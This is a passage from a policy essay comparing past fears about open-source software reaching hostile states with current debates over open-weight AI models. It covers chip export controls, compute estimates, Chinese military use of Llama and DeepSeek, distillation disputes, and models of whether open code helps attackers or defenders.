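China came closest to fulfilling the forecast. In November 2010, Tianhe-1A, a computer in Tianjin, took first place on the TOP500. The Chinese military's National University of Defense Technology had built it with 14,336 processors from Intel and 7,168 graphics chips from Nvidia, both American companies. The same university's Tianhe-2 held first place from June 2013 until 2016. Both computers ran versions of Linux.

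So a state adversary had used a free operating system to run the world's fastest known computer. But the builders had bought more than 20,000 American chips for the first machine alone, and they had designed their own network to connect them, which is the hard part of the airflow example. A lone expert with some office PCs could have downloaded the same operating system but could not have built a computer nearly as fast.

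Iran's case looks more like McBride's scenario. In December 2007 a research centre at Amirkabir University in Tehran announced a Linux cluster with 216 processors made by the American company AMD, despite the US embargo. The centre said it would use the machine for weather research. AMD said it had never authorised any shipment to Iran, so the chips had presumably come through a middleman. The cluster's theoretical speed was 860 billion calculations a second, about a seventh of what a computer then needed to get onto the TOP500. The software was free, but Iran still had to get the processors past the embargo.

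North Korea did adopt Linux. The state-run Korea Computer Center adapted it into an operating system called Red Star. Two German researchers, Florian Grunow and Niklaus Schiess, analyzed a leaked copy and presented their findings in December 2015. They found that it added a hidden mark to documents and media files, which would let the authorities trace files between computers, and that it restarted the machine if a user tampered with certain system files. The best-documented North Korean use of Linux is therefore domestic surveillance. No North Korean supercomputer has appeared on the TOP500 list, but this proves little, since owners enter their machines voluntarily and a weapons laboratory has good reasons not to.

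By November 2017 all 500 computers on the list ran Linux. The American weapons laboratories used it, and so did every adversary with a supercomputer on the list, which McBride could have claimed as a vindication of his warning. Linux gave no country a lead because they all had it. The differences between countries came from the number and quality of their chips, the networks connecting them and the skill of the people running the machines.

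### Washington restricts the chips

American officials came to see the problem similarly. In February 2015 the Commerce Department added the National University of Defense Technology and the supercomputing centres in Changsha, Guangzhou and Tianjin to its Entity List because it believed the Tianhe machines were contributing to work on nuclear weapons. Foreign organisations on the list need a licence to receive American goods, and Intel could no longer supply the chips for a planned upgrade of Tianhe-2.

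The university designed a replacement chip and finished the upgrade late. In 2016 another Chinese computer, Sunway TaihuLight, took first place on the TOP500 with 40,960 processors designed in China. The 2015 restrictions may have encouraged such work, but they can't have led to the Sunway project, which was already under way.

In April 2021 Commerce listed seven more Chinese organisations, four of them supercomputing centres and the others chip designers. One of the chip designers, Phytium, relied on the Taiwanese company TSMC to manufacture the processors it designed, and TSMC stopped taking its orders. China had engineers who could design a good processor but few factories that could make one.

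The October 2022 rules went much further, restricting sales of advanced AI chips to all Chinese buyers, along with machinery for making advanced chips and American parts for any very large Chinese supercomputer. The new rule covered chips that exceeded two thresholds, one for calculation speed and one for the speed of data exchange with other chips. The second threshold addressed the weakness of the old MTOPS limit, which did not measure how well machines could work together. Nvidia responded by selling China a version of its leading chip with slower connections, and a year later Commerce dropped the connection threshold and relied on measures of computing power alone.

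None of these measures restricted Linux. Zeitouni (2022), in *Milling the F/Loss*, argues that the government forced free and open-source software into an export-control framework that suited it poorly, and describes how the rules came to leave it out. China's supercomputing centres could therefore keep downloading each new Linux release while Washington tried to cut off their supply of processors to run it.

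Senator Warner's office (2025) made a new version of McBride's argument in a letter to the Commerce Department's export-control bureau about RISC-V, a freely published instruction set (the list of basic commands a processor can carry out). Anyone may design a chip around RISC-V without buying a licence from a company such as Arm. According to the letter, Chinese leaders regard open-source technology as a key way around American and allied controls. This argument is stronger than McBride's because a Chinese company that cannot license a foreign design gains something from a free one, but the company still needs a factory to make the chip, as Phytium did.

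Hardware controls also have gaps. In January 2002, American officials had yet to carry out more than 700 checks on how Chinese buyers were using exported computers, and Beijing decided when they could do so. FDD Action's *NDAA AI Export Controls Coalition Letter* (2026) lists the current ways around the controls as smuggling, renting computers abroad over the internet, and making chips in China with equipment from allied countries. It also lists distillation, which means training one model on the outputs of another to copy part of its ability at lower cost. FDD Action lobbies for stricter controls, so its claim that the existing ones have held back Chinese AI companies should be treated with some caution. However, Chinese developers would have little reason to use these methods if they could easily get all the computing power they wanted.

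McBride was right that export controls could not keep a good operating system from a hostile state. But restricting open source would have done very little to limit foreign supercomputers, because software was the one component nobody was short of. The US government had more effect on the problem once it restricted access to chips.

Many people now want to use similar export controls to protect the American lead in AI. Dmitri Alperovitch, who chairs the think tank Silverado Policy Accelerator, told a House committee in April 2026 that selling China the best AI chips was like "selling rockets to the Soviets during the moon race", according to Bloomberg Law's *Congress Urged to Pass Stricter AI Export Controls Against China* (2026). Downloading Linux gave the recipient no extra processors, but a developer who publishes model weights has already used the computing power needed to train the model,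 so the recipient doesn't have to repeat the training. How much open weights weaken chip controls therefore depends on which input to AI is scarce and how much of it a hostile state gets with the download.

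## What a hostile state gains by downloading a model

An AI developer needs chips to train a model and to run it, and American export controls make both harder for China. A Chinese army unit that downloads a model someone else has trained needs chips only to run it.

### The computing power inside the weights

Two rules of thumb show how much the unit saves. A language model reads and writes text in tokens, pieces that average somewhat less than a word. To process one token, the computer multiplies each weight it uses by another number and adds the result to a running total, which makes two operations per weight. In training, the computer must also work out how to adjust each weight, which takes about four more. If *N* is the number of weights in use for any one token and *D* is the number of tokens in the training text, then

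training ≈ 6 × *N* × *D* operations,

running ≈ 2 × *N* operations per token.

*N* can be much smaller than the total number of weights. Many large models are "mixtures of experts", which divide most of their weights into groups and use only a few groups for each token. *DeepSeek-V4* (2026), a technical report by the Chinese developer DeepSeek, gives the figures for one such model, V4-Pro. It has 1.6 trillion weights, of which 49 billion are active for each token, and DeepSeek trained it on 33 trillion tokens. The training therefore took about

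6 × 49 billion × 33 trillion ≈ 9.7 × 10^24 operations,

while running the model takes about 98 billion operations per token.

If an Nvidia H100 chip sustains 4 × 10^14 operations a second, it would need about 770 years to repeat the training of DeepSeek's V4-Pro, and a thousand chips would need a little over nine months. A state that downloads the model avoids this computation. It would have to run 99 trillion tokens through V4-Pro, three times the length of the training text, before it had used as much computing power as DeepSeek used for training.

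The estimate is rough and probably too low, because it leaves out experiments and the later rounds of training that teach a model to follow instructions and solve problems. Epoch AI's *Keeping up with the GPTs* (2026), an essay from a research group that tracks AI computing, reports that AI companies spend most of their computing budget on experiments rather than final training runs. The downloader also benefits from DeepSeek's failed experiments, without learning what they were.

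### What the download leaves out

First, the unit lacks the hardware to run the model. V4-Pro takes up about 800 gigabytes at half a byte per weight, and an H100 chip has 80 gigabytes of memory, so the unit needs at least ten of these chips to load it. In July 2026, the Beijing company Moonshot AI released a larger model, Kimi K3. It has 2.8 trillion weights, with 104 billion active for each token, according to *Kimi K3*, the page that accompanies the weights. It needs about 18 H100s to hold it and twice as much calculation per token as V4-Pro.

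A research group can find 18 chips, but an army that wants everybody to use the model would have more trouble finding enough. If 100,000 staff each put ten million tokens a day through V4-Pro, they would keep nearly 3,000 H100s busy around the clock at the rate assumed above. That much use is plausible once models carry out long tasks on their own. In practice the army would need more chips, because chips generating text spend much of their time waiting for data from memory. Chip controls therefore still limit how much a state can use a free model, though the state may not have to rely on American chips. Yicai Global's *Moonshot AI Says Kimi K3 Is World's First Open-Source 3T-Class Model* reports that Moonshot tested K3 on other companies' processors as well as Nvidia's.

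The downloader also lacks the training data and, as *Beyond the Binary* (Özcan, Petropoulos and Reddel, 2025) points out, often the full code. Moonshot published more than most developers do, including some of its training software and, according to Neurohive's *Kimi K3 Review*, a description of how it collected its data, but it did not publish the data itself. An engineer can learn a good deal from this, but to build a better successor she would still need her own data, a large number of chips, and colleagues who know from experience what goes wrong in a months-long training run.

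### Five routes to the same ability

The marginal risk of the download depends on the state's other options. Kapoor, Bommasani and colleagues (2024), in *On the Societal Impact of Open Foundation Models*, worked out a method for assessing the marginal risk of open-weight models, with closed models and older technology such as web search as the baseline. *Towards a Framework for Openness in Foundation Models* (2024), the proceedings of a meeting at Columbia University, lists their six steps:

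1. Specify the threat: who would do what, and how.
2. Work out the existing risk without open models.
3. Work out the existing defences.
4. Give evidence of the risk that releasing the weights adds.
5. Ask how hard it would be to defend against the added risk.
6. State the assumptions and uncertainties.

Kapoor and colleagues looked at seven kinds of misuse, including scams, disinformation and biological weapons, and found that in most cases earlier studies had not properly assessed how much risk open models add. Their examples are mostly things a criminal or small group might do. A government has more alternatives than a criminal, so the same model should usually help it less.

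An army unit that wants to translate and summarise captured documents without any foreign company seeing them could get a model in five ways.

| Route | What the state needs | What it gets | What can stop it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Train its own model | Thousands of advanced chips, data, experienced engineers | Full control, and the means to build the next model | Chip controls |
| Steal closed weights | A spy in the company or a way into its network | The closed model itself, perhaps before its release | The developer's security |
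| Distil a closed model | Accounts with the developer's service, and chips to train on its answers | A weaker model that it can run in private | Blocking the accounts, until the state opens new ones |
| Use a closed model as a customer | An account, perhaps through a front company | The best model on sale, with its safeguards | The developer can read the requests and close the account |
| Download open weights | Chips to run the model | A slightly older model that it can run in private, alter and keep | Once the weights are out, only a shortage of chips |

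A customer account is useless for working with the captured documents because the developer could read them. Downloading the model solves that problem cheaply. Kapoor and colleagues list local use among the distinctive properties of open models, along with the developer's inability to monitor how a model is used or take it back. Running a model locally lets an intelligence service keep its documents private, much as it lets a hospital protect patients' records.

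The gain also depends on the state. Chinese companies train models nearly as good as the American ones, so downloading an American model saves China's army little. Iran and North Korea have no comparable models that are publicly known. For them, a download replaces nearly all of the 9.7 × 10^24 operations, and the alternatives are to steal a model or use one through an account that its American provider can close. But they can download a Chinese model as easily as an American one, so an American developer that keeps its weights private denies them only the difference in capability between the two.

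The weakness of this way of counting is that each release becomes part of the baseline for the next. If ten developers in turn each publish a model slightly better than the last, each can truthfully say that its release added little, even though a state that could do almost nothing at the start can do a great deal by the end. The method of Kapoor and colleagues works for judging a single release, but it needs a fixed starting date to measure what a policy of open release has given hostile states over several years.

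### From Llama to DeepSeek in the Chinese armed forces

In November 2024 Reuters reported the first well-documented case of military researchers building on an American open model, in a story that Dawn carried as *Chinese researchers develop AI model for military use* (2024). Six Chinese researchers, some of them from two institutes of the army's Academy of Military Science, had described a system called ChatBIT in a paper. They fine-tuned Meta's Llama 2 13B, a 13-billion-weight model released in 2023, on 100,000 records of military dialogue so that it could answer questions and help gather intelligence. They wrote that it did better than some models with roughly 90 per cent of GPT-4's ability, but did not explain how they measured this or say whether anyone was using the system.

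Meta's licence prohibited military use, and the company called the work unauthorised. It added that a "single, and outdated" American model was irrelevant when China was, by Meta's account, investing a trillion dollars in AI. Joelle Pineau, then a Meta vice president, doubted that 100,000 records could have achieved much, since models normally learn from trillions of tokens. But Meta had already trained the model on trillions of tokens, so the researchers who downloaded it could make do with far less text.

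Meta trained Llama 2 on about 2 trillion tokens, so by the same rule the 13-billion-weight version took about 1.6 × 10^23 operations, a sixtieth of V4-Pro's total. A hundred H100s could do that in about six weeks. China's armed forces, whose engineers had built the world's fastest supercomputer, could probably have found equivalent computing power. The download saved the ChatBIT team time and money, and perhaps they would not have tried the idea without it, but it did not give China an ability it could not have developed itself. Just Security's *The United States Must Win The Global Open Source AI Race* made a similar reply to the alarm in Washington, noting that Chinese companies already had models as good as the American open ones.

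Two researchers at the state aircraft maker AVIC described using Llama 2 to train strategies for jamming enemy electronics from the air, and another paper covered its use in policing. Military interest then moved to Chinese models. Cheung and Lau (2025), in *DeepSeek Use in PRC Military and Public Security Systems*, found in procurement documents that the Chinese armed forces were adopting DeepSeek and other domestic systems, though some powerful institutions doubted their usefulness. Reuters, in an October 2025 story carried by BusinessWorld, saw a dozen military tenders from that year that mentioned DeepSeek and only one that mentioned Alibaba's Qwen. In February 2025 the state arms maker Norinco unveiled a support vehicle that ran on DeepSeek and could drive itself at 50 kilometres an hour, according to TechCentral's *How Beijing's army of robot dogs and AI drones could redefine warfare*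 (2025).

The most detailed account is in *The National Security Case for Limiting China's Access to Advanced U.S. Compute*, by McFaul and Bresnick of CSET, who had reviewed thousands of AI-related procurement documents from three years. In August 2025 one unit asked for a DeepSeek system to translate, extract information from documents, analyse flight paths and compare images. Others wanted DeepSeek to help control groups of unmanned vehicles, support "psychological attack" and propaganda, and take part in computer-intrusion exercises.

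The tenders show that military units want the same ready-made models as everybody else, often for dull clerical work. But a tender is only a request, so we cannot tell from it whether the supplier delivered, whether the system worked, or whether the unit ever used it for anything that mattered. McFaul and Bresnick say that they cannot measure how widely the armed forces have adopted AI. Secret projects would presumably not appear in public tenders at all.

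A state that downloads a free model still needs chips to run it. In May 2025 a Chinese military laboratory asked for sixteen Nvidia H100s, which American companies may not sell to China without a licence, to run "DeepSeek-70B" and Alibaba's Qwen-32B in research on electromagnetic and infrared signatures. The DeepSeek model is probably one that DeepSeek made by training Meta's Llama on the answers of its own R1 model, which would make it partly American too. Jensen Huang, Nvidia's chief executive, has argued that the Chinese armed forces cannot rely on American chips and do not need them. McFaul and Bresnick found hundreds of requests for American AI hardware between 2023 and 2026, as well as many tenders that required Chinese products.

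McFaul and Bresnick conclude that slowing China's commercial AI companies also slows its armed forces, because the companies train the models that the armed forces use. This seems right, and it means that open weights only partly explain how those forces get their models. DeepSeek is a Chinese company, so the Chinese army would very likely have got its model even if DeepSeek had never released it publicly.

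### How old is the model that anyone can download?

A free model's value depends on how far it trails the best closed models. Raschka (2026) measured this gap on 3 December in *How Far Behind Are Open-Weight Models?*. For each open model, he counted back from the day its developer published the weights to the first day a publicly available closed model had scored as well on an index that combines many tests.

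| Open-weight model | Developer | Days behind when the weights came out |
|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 405B | Meta, US | 71 |
| DeepSeek-R1 | DeepSeek, China | 130 |
| Kimi K3 | Moonshot, China | 95 |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro | Moonshot, China | 64 |
| Amazon Ergo | Amazon, US | 175 |

Llama 3.1 came out in July 2024 and Kimi K3.1 Pro in November 2026, so on this measure the gap hardly changed in more than two years. The gap also grows every day until the next release. By 3 December Kimi K3.1 Pro was 93 days behind. It scored 337, against 368 for the leader, Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.2.

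Other estimates are longer. Epoch AI puts the average gap between Chinese and American models since 2023 at seven months, with a range from four to fourteen. DeepSeek judged in its technical report that V4-Pro trailed the best closed models by three to six months in reasoning. In September, Tom's Hardware's *China's open-weight AI models are now just 4 months behind* reported a Mozilla estimate. Two months later, the same publication's *Beijing's AI ambitions are under threat as models may fall behind* (Ahmed, 2026) reported that the gap could reach nine months. The estimates differ partly because they use different tests. Public tests also tend to make the trailing models look closer than they are, since developers can train for them. In *On Kimi K3*, the writer Zvi Mowshowitz thought K3's practical performance was less surprising than its scores, and noted that a preliminary rating put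 it exactly on the existing Chinese trend line.

All these comparisons use models the public can buy. Raschka notes that companies may have reached the same scores earlier with private models, so a state that downloads the best open model may be more than 93 days behind the best American laboratory.

A three-month gap makes no difference for translating captured documents, because once a model does the job well enough, an army can keep using it for years. The gap matters more where two sides compete directly, such as when one searches software for vulnerabilities and the other tries to fix them first.

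The countries in the table matter more for the old objection than the number of days. McBride and the critics of Llama feared that Americans would publish something valuable and foreigners would take it. By December 2026 the best open-weight model was Chinese, and the best American one was about three months further behind. American companies now download Chinese models. Fortune (2026) reports that Cursor, which makes a programming assistant, built one of its products partly on Kimi, that the delivery company DoorDash gave Kimi some of its simpler work, and that the AI developer Thinking Machines used it to produce training data. Just Security's *Amid the Open-Source AI Debate, America Needs a New Theory* reports that Chinese models made up 41 per cent of the past year's model downloads on Hugging Face, the main site for sharing models.

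An American rule against publishing weights would therefore have little effect on the Chinese armed forces. It might have mattered in 2023, when Llama was better than what most Chinese companies could make, but officials would have had to act then, before anyone had shown that the models were useful to an army.

### Distillation and the accusations of 2026

To distil a model, a developer sends it many questions and trains another model on the answers, which doesn't require the original's weights. Distillation is common. DeepSeek's report describes how the company trained separate specialist models for mathematics, programming and other subjects, then distilled them into one. American companies probably make their cheaper "mini" models in a similar way. The practice becomes contentious when a developer distils a competitor's model in violation of the competitor's terms.

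By April 2026 Anthropic had accused three Chinese developers, DeepSeek, Moonshot and MiniMax, of training on answers from its Claude models. According to Epoch AI, MiniMax may have collected about 100 billion tokens from Claude. That is far less than the 33 trillion tokens in V4-Pro's training text, but developers have used only about 4 billion tokens to distill DeepSeek-R1's reasoning into other models.

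Moonshot's president, Yutong Zhang, gave a different explanation for the company's progress at the World Economic Forum in 2026, saying that Moonshot could not "simply scale up compute" and so had to concentrate on research and efficiency. This doesn't contradict Anthropic's accusation, since a company can do original research and also copy a competitor's answers. Older evidence of copying is weak. In 2024, Alibaba's Qwen sometimes identified itself as Claude, but a model can learn to do this from Claude's output that other people have posted on the web.

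According to Epoch AI's essay, the leading American companies have around ten times as much computing power as their Chinese competitors. Its author thinks distillation could cut the computing a company needs several-fold, and guesses that this narrows the gap without closing it. The size of the student model also matters. When DeepSeek distilled R1 into smaller models, the version with 32 billion weights scored 72.6 per cent on a mathematics competition, compared with 79.8 per cent for R1 and 28.9 per cent for the version with 1.5 billion. Distilled models may also do worse outside the subjects covered by the questions used to train them, and a developer who wants strong reasoning still has to let its model learn by trial and error, which takes chips.

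Distillation, which trains one model on another's outputs, weakens the case for keeping weights private because it works on closed models too. If Anthropic's accusations against Moonshot are right, some of Claude's ability is now also available to Iran and North Korea, because Moonshot publishes its weights. Anthropic could in principle close the accounts Moonshot allegedly used, but nobody can block downloads of the weights.

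### The July 2026 letter and Amodei's reply

After Kimi K3 appeared in mid-July 2026, alarmed officials in Washington discussed measures against Chinese open models. On 24 July American companies published a letter, Microsoft's *Open Weights and American AI Leadership* (2026), asking the government not to restrict open weights. Nvidia, Microsoft, Meta and more than 200 other organisations signed it, but Anthropic did not. Axios' *Anthropic CEO Dario Amodei says he does not support open-weight AI ban* reports that Google and OpenAI, which make most of their AI money from closed models, stayed out at first but signed over the weekend.

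The letter opens with the 1980s, when the pioneers of open-source software challenged the belief that software would advance only if companies kept tight control of their code. Their work now supports most of the internet, the systems of the largest technology companies, and the American armed forces. The signatories argue that the United States "now faces a similar choice" with AI, and that open weights would let small companies build on advanced models without training one, keep prices down, and free customers from dependence on a single supplier. They concede that developers can't control weights after publishing them and that altered versions are hard to trace. But they think defenders against cyberattacks need models as good as the attackers', and that a few closed models would become single points of failure. They also defend distillation as a normal technique and want narrow legal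 remedies for unlawful uses of it.

The letter is right that open-source software became indispensable, including to the armed forces that O'Dowd wanted to protect from it. But it never mentions China or any other hostile government, though a Chinese model prompted it, and its comparison of open-weight models to open-source software fails on the point that matters most to an adversary. The harm McBride warned of mostly did not materialize because Linux contained nothing that a hostile state was short of. Model weights are the product of computing power, which China is short of and which Iran and North Korea mostly lack.

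The signatories could have made a better argument. The strongest open models are already Chinese, so stopping American companies from publishing would deprive hostile states of very little, and foreign customers who want an open model would be left with a Chinese one. *Amid the Open-Source AI Debate* made this case in August, arguing that such a restriction probably could not slow Chinese progress. Much like Karn's argument about encryption, this one relies on foreign availability. It would lose most of its force if an American developer were about to publish a model clearly better than anything from China.

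Dario Amodei, the chief executive of Anthropic, replied on 27 July, the day Moonshot posted K3's weights. He wrote that Anthropic had never advocated a ban on open-weight models, and called those without dangerous capabilities "a public good". He mainly feared that an authoritarian government would build models more powerful than the American ones and use them for permanent military superiority or for extreme repression at home. He wrote that whether it published the weights was "irrelevant" to this danger, and that the most dangerous model might be one that a developer trained in secret and gave only to the Chinese army and security services.

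His lesser fear was that people would use powerful models for cyberattacks or biological attacks, or that the models themselves would behave dangerously. He thought open-weight models were probably riskier in this respect, since nobody can monitor their use or recall them. But he argued that banning American companies from using Chinese models would not help, because the attackers "are unlikely to be legitimate US businesses". He proposed instead keeping advanced chips and chipmaking equipment from China, stopping industrial-scale distillation, and requiring safety tests for all sufficiently capable models, open or closed. He also rejected the letter's claims that open weights necessarily make safeguards easier to develop and that broad access necessarily helps defenders more than attackers. His counterexample was biology, where an attacker might turn a virus into a weapon quickly but a defence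 takes years.

Amodei is right about the case he describes. An army with its own secret model does not need to download one, and no state can overtake the United States merely by downloading what Americans can download too. But "irrelevant" is a little too strong, because openness may help China build such a model sooner. *Two Loops* (Luong, 2026), a paper for a commission that advises Congress on China, argues that open release lets Chinese companies work close to the frontier despite having few chips. Other developers adopt the models and improve them, which attracts more users. Chinese companies also borrow from one another. K3, for example, uses a version of multi-head latent attention, a memory-saving design that DeepSeek invented. Published papers would spread many of these methods even if every company kept its weights private, so it is hard to say how much of the effect comes from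 releasing the weights.

Amodei's argument depends more heavily on the claim that China cannot build better models than the United States without American chips. K3 casts some doubt on that claim. Moonshot, a company of about 300 people, released K3 only days after the research firm SemiAnalysis had called Chinese laboratories "simply too compute poor to truly reach the frontier", according to The Decoder. The model matched one of Anthropic's recent best. K3 still fell short of the leading models from Anthropic and OpenAI, and Epoch AI has found no Chinese model in first place since 2023, so the record fits Amodei's prediction that China will stay behind. But a company with a tenth of the chips that ends up three months behind is little reassurance to anyone who worries about what the Chinese army can do, rather than whether it can do more than the American one.

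David Sacks, a White House adviser on AI, was among those who accused Anthropic of using safety to protect its business. Anthropic sells access to closed models, and a free model that is nearly as good limits what it can charge. Amodei conceded that a ban would shield American AI companies from competition, but said this had never been his goal. His three measures would also help Anthropic. Chip controls hold back its Chinese competitors, and a crackdown on distillation protects its product directly. Mandatory tests could burden open models more, because only a closed developer can promise to watch for misuse after release.

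On the other hand, he publicly opposed the ban, the measure that would have helped Anthropic most directly. Google and OpenAI also sell closed models but signed the letter, so selling closed models does not determine which side a company takes. The signatories had commercial interests too. Nvidia sells the chips that open models run on, and Microsoft and Amazon rent out those chips. Outsiders can check the claim about chips against Epoch AI's figures and the Chinese army's tenders. The claim about distillation is much harder for them to check, because the main evidence is in the complaining company's records.

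## Whether readable code helps attackers more than defenders

McBride and the critics of Llama worried about foreigners running what Americans had published. Kenneth Brown worried about attackers reading it.

### The white paper and its press release

The Alexis de Tocqueville Institution announced Brown's white paper on 30 May 2002, less than nine months after the attacks of 11 September. In the press release that McCullagh forwarded, the institution warned that open source could help terrorists sabotage electronic commerce, air traffic control or "even sensitive surveillance systems". The paper itself is less alarming. Brown spends most of it on what the GPL would do to software companies, and his chapter on security discusses hackers and adversaries but never mentions terrorists. He returns to national security in the fourth of his eight closing points, where he calls government use of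 such software "exceptionally risky".

In *Fighting terrorism with obscurity*, Bradner (2002) called it "intellectually dishonest" to use the threat of terrorism to sell an unrelated topic. By then the institution had withdrawn the paper, saying it had posted the wrong version. In *Response to Mr. Brown's critique of Open Source Software*, Ambrose (2002) noticed that the withdrawn version credited the American software industry with 319 million jobs, more than the country's population. Brown reworded other passages that Ambrose had criticised but kept the jobs figure.

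Still, the paper argues that an attacker can get an exact copy of the code an agency runs and search it at leisure. He can follow the public forums where programmers discuss faults, and perhaps learn of a weakness before the agency has fixed it. He can also learn from the code how the defences work. Brown quotes Jason Rexilius, a former Air Force intelligence analyst, who imagined an intruder posing as a janitor with five minutes to break into a closed network. If the blueprints were public, the intruder could have built a replica beforehand and prepared his tools on it. Rexilius added that none of this would matter against a well-built system.

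Others Brown quotes disagreed with him. Wheeler asked why an attacker would need a building's blueprint when he could get an exact copy of the building and search that. Anyone can buy a commercial program and then feed it many odd inputs, or use a decompiler to turn it back into rough source code. Brown conceded that decompiling recovers much of the source. He also described the GPL's requirements imprecisely. The license requires an agency to share source code only with people it gives the program to, so the Federal Aviation Administration could adapt Linux for its own control rooms and keep the changes secret.

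### Allchin's testimony and Microsoft's guests

Microsoft made a similar argument in court that May. Nine states and the District of Columbia wanted stricter penalties in the company's antitrust case, including an order to disclose more about how Windows works with other software. Jim Allchin, the Microsoft executive in charge of Windows, testified that such disclosures would help hackers, that the armed forces were using Windows in Afghanistan, and that it was "no exaggeration" to bring national security into it (Carlson, 2002, *Allchin*).

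The dispute was over interfaces (the commands other programs use to call on Windows) and protocols (the rules for exchanging messages between computers). Under questioning, Allchin could name only one protocol that Microsoft expected to withhold. It belonged to the Message Queuing feature and contained a mistake that would endanger customers if Microsoft published the details. The Register's *Allchin quizzed on 'secret' MS protocols and APIs* contrasts this with the evidence of Roger Needham, who ran Microsoft's research laboratory in Cambridge. Needham thought the company needed to protect only cryptographic keys and their locations.

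Allchin's argument justified delaying disclosure but not permanent secrecy, because nobody should advertise a flaw before repairing it, and Microsoft was already replacing the faulty protocol. He also admitted that outsiders had worked out an unpublished part of Microsoft's copy-protection system by taking the software apart. According to eWeek's *On Guard*, he testified that exposing code to extensive peer review had produced the safest code available.

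Eight months later, on 14 January 2003, Microsoft announced its Government Security Program, which let foreign governments see the source code of Windows (Microsoft, 2003). NATO and Russia were among the first to join. The Russian signatory acted for FAPSI, the agency that protected Russia's official communications and intercepted those of other countries. China joined on 28 February, and Bill Gates briefed President Jiang Zemin on the agreement, according to Microsoft (2003). Officials could read the code online with a smart card, under a restrictive licence. The program had about 30 signatories by September 2004, according to Redmond Channel Partner's *Government Source Code Review Program Expanded to Office* (2004).

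China also got a laboratory in Beijing for reading the code. Microsoft's *China Information Technology Security Certification Center Source Code Review Lab Opened* (2003) names seven Chinese partners that shared the access, including the security company Topsec. According to a leaked American diplomatic cable from 2009, Topsec had once employed a well-known hacker. In 2017 the security firm Recorded Future identified the certification centre as part of the Ministry of State Security, China's main civilian intelligence service. There is no public evidence that anyone used the programme to break into American computers. But experts working for two state adversaries could now study proprietary Microsoft code that the Pentagon ran, which is the kind of access Brown had feared.

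### Why the two effects might cancel

That same year, Ross Anderson, a computer scientist at Cambridge, gave a theoretical answer in *Security in Open versus Closed Systems*. He quotes Brown's white paper for the view that openness helps attackers, and also presents the opposing view that it helps defenders. He shows that under ideal conditions, openness helps both equally.

Suppose a program has many flaws, and that random testing hits a particular flaw *r* times an hour on average. The chance that nobody has hit it after *t* hours is e^(−*rt*), so the flaw contributes *r*e^(−*rt*) to the rate at which testers run into new trouble. Some flaws show themselves in minutes and others take centuries. Anderson and two colleagues had argued that in a large, well-tested program the number of flaws with rates near *r* is roughly *K*/*r*, where *K* depends on how good the code was to begin with. In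 other words, about as many flaws take between 10 and 100 hours to find as take between 100 and 1,000. Adding up all the contributions gives

failure rate = ∫ (*K*/*r*) × *r*e^(−*rt*) d*r* = *K*/*t*.

If *K* is 1, then after 10,000 hours of testing and repair, the next flaw takes about 10,000 hours to find.

If hiding the source code makes every flaw λ times harder to find, the defenders' *t* hours of testing achieve only as much as *t*/λ hours would with readable code. The program they release would therefore fail at a rate of λ*K*/*t* for anyone who could read the code. But the attacker can't read it either, so he works λ times more slowly and finds flaws at a rate of *K*/*t*. If the code is published, the defenders' testing cuts the failure rate by a factor of λ, but the attacker searches λ times faster, so he finds his next flaw just as soon as he would with the code hidden.

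Anderson, in *Open and Closed Systems are Equivalent (that is, in an ideal world)*, cites an estimate that λ lies between 3 and 5 for mature software. The formula also covers cases where only one side can read the code. With λ = 4 and 10,000 hours of testing, it gives these results:

| Defenders test with the source code | Attacker has the source code | Hours until the attacker finds a flaw |
|---|---|---|
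| Yes | Yes | 10,000 |
| No | No | 10,000 |
| Yes | No | 40,000 |
| No | Yes | 2,500 |

A software company would say that it belongs in the third row, because its own programmers test with the source code. Anderson replied that a few dozen employees do much less of the testing than the tens of thousands of outsiders who try a preliminary version without the source. If he was right, showing the Windows source code to Russia and China moved Windows towards the fourth row for those two countries.

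The cancellation depends on several assumptions:

- The program has enough flaws for averages to mean something.
- The flaws are independent, so finding one does not help with the next.
- Both sides search at random, and the source code speeds them up by the same factor.
- Somebody repairs each flaw as soon as a defender finds it, without adding new ones.

Anderson did not think real software met all of these conditions. He wanted to draw attention to the ways it departs from them, some of which matter a good deal when the attacker is a government. Volunteers are unlikely to check the Linux code for smartcard readers as closely as an enemy government might. A large supply of rare flaws also favours attackers, whether or not the code is public. If a program has a million flaws that each take a billion hours to find, an attacker will find one of them in about 1,000 hours. A defender who searches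 for a million hours will find about 1,000 flaws, with a one-in-a-thousand chance that the attacker's flaw is among them.

In *A Model for When Disclosure Helps Security* (2004), Peter Swire, a law professor who had advised the Clinton administration on privacy, compares how much a disclosure helps attackers with how much it improves the defence. Armies keep their plans secret because publishing them would help the enemy a lot and their own side little, whereas open-source programmers assume that publishing code mostly helps defenders. Sometimes both effects are large, as when companies warn each other about a new attack, and sometimes both are small because everybody already knows the facts.

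Swire argues that secrecy works best against a first attack. A hidden trap may catch the first intruder, but someone who can keep coming back will learn where it is. Attackers can try mass-market software thousands of times on their own computers with almost no effort, so hiding its design protects it relatively little. The case for secrecy is therefore much stronger against Rexilius's janitor, who gets one visit to one building, than against an anonymous hacker who has a copy of Windows at home.

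Disclosure helps defenders most when a program has many unknown users, nobody can privately contact the friendly ones, and no commander can order them all to install a fix. These conditions hold for Linux but not for the software in a missile, which has one owner and which a foreign attacker may never have handled.

### Counting flaws

Anderson's formula predicts that software becomes safer slowly. In *Is finding security holes a good idea?*, Rescorla looked for this improvement in public records of vulnerabilities, including some in Windows NT 4.0 and the Unix system Solaris 2.5.1. He could not rule out that people kept finding flaws in a given version at a constant rate for years.

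If so, repairing a flaw may do less good than programmers assume, because the announcement tells every attacker about it while many computers remain unrepaired. Rescorla put this as an inequality. Let *p* be the chance that an attacker would have found the flaw anyway, *A* the cost of break-ins while only attackers know of it, and *B* the cost of break-ins after everyone does. Disclosing the flaw reduces the expected cost only if

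*p* × (*A* + *B*) > *B*.

If the secret break-ins would cost a quarter as much as the public ones, *p* must be above 80 per cent.

A longer record of a single system gave more encouraging results. In *Milk or Wine* (2006), Ozment and Schechter traced 140 vulnerabilities through 15 versions of OpenBSD, a free operating system whose developers are unusually strict about security, over seven and a half years. Code unchanged since the first version they examined still made up 61 per cent of the system and accounted for 62 per cent of the vulnerabilities. People reported flaws in this old code less and less often, although the median flaw survived at least 2.6 years. In *Does OpenBSD and Firefox's Security Improve with Time?*, Shi, Zou and colleagues extended the record to 22 years and added nine years of the Firefox browser. Both programs became more secure, but their newer developers did not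 necessarily write safer code.

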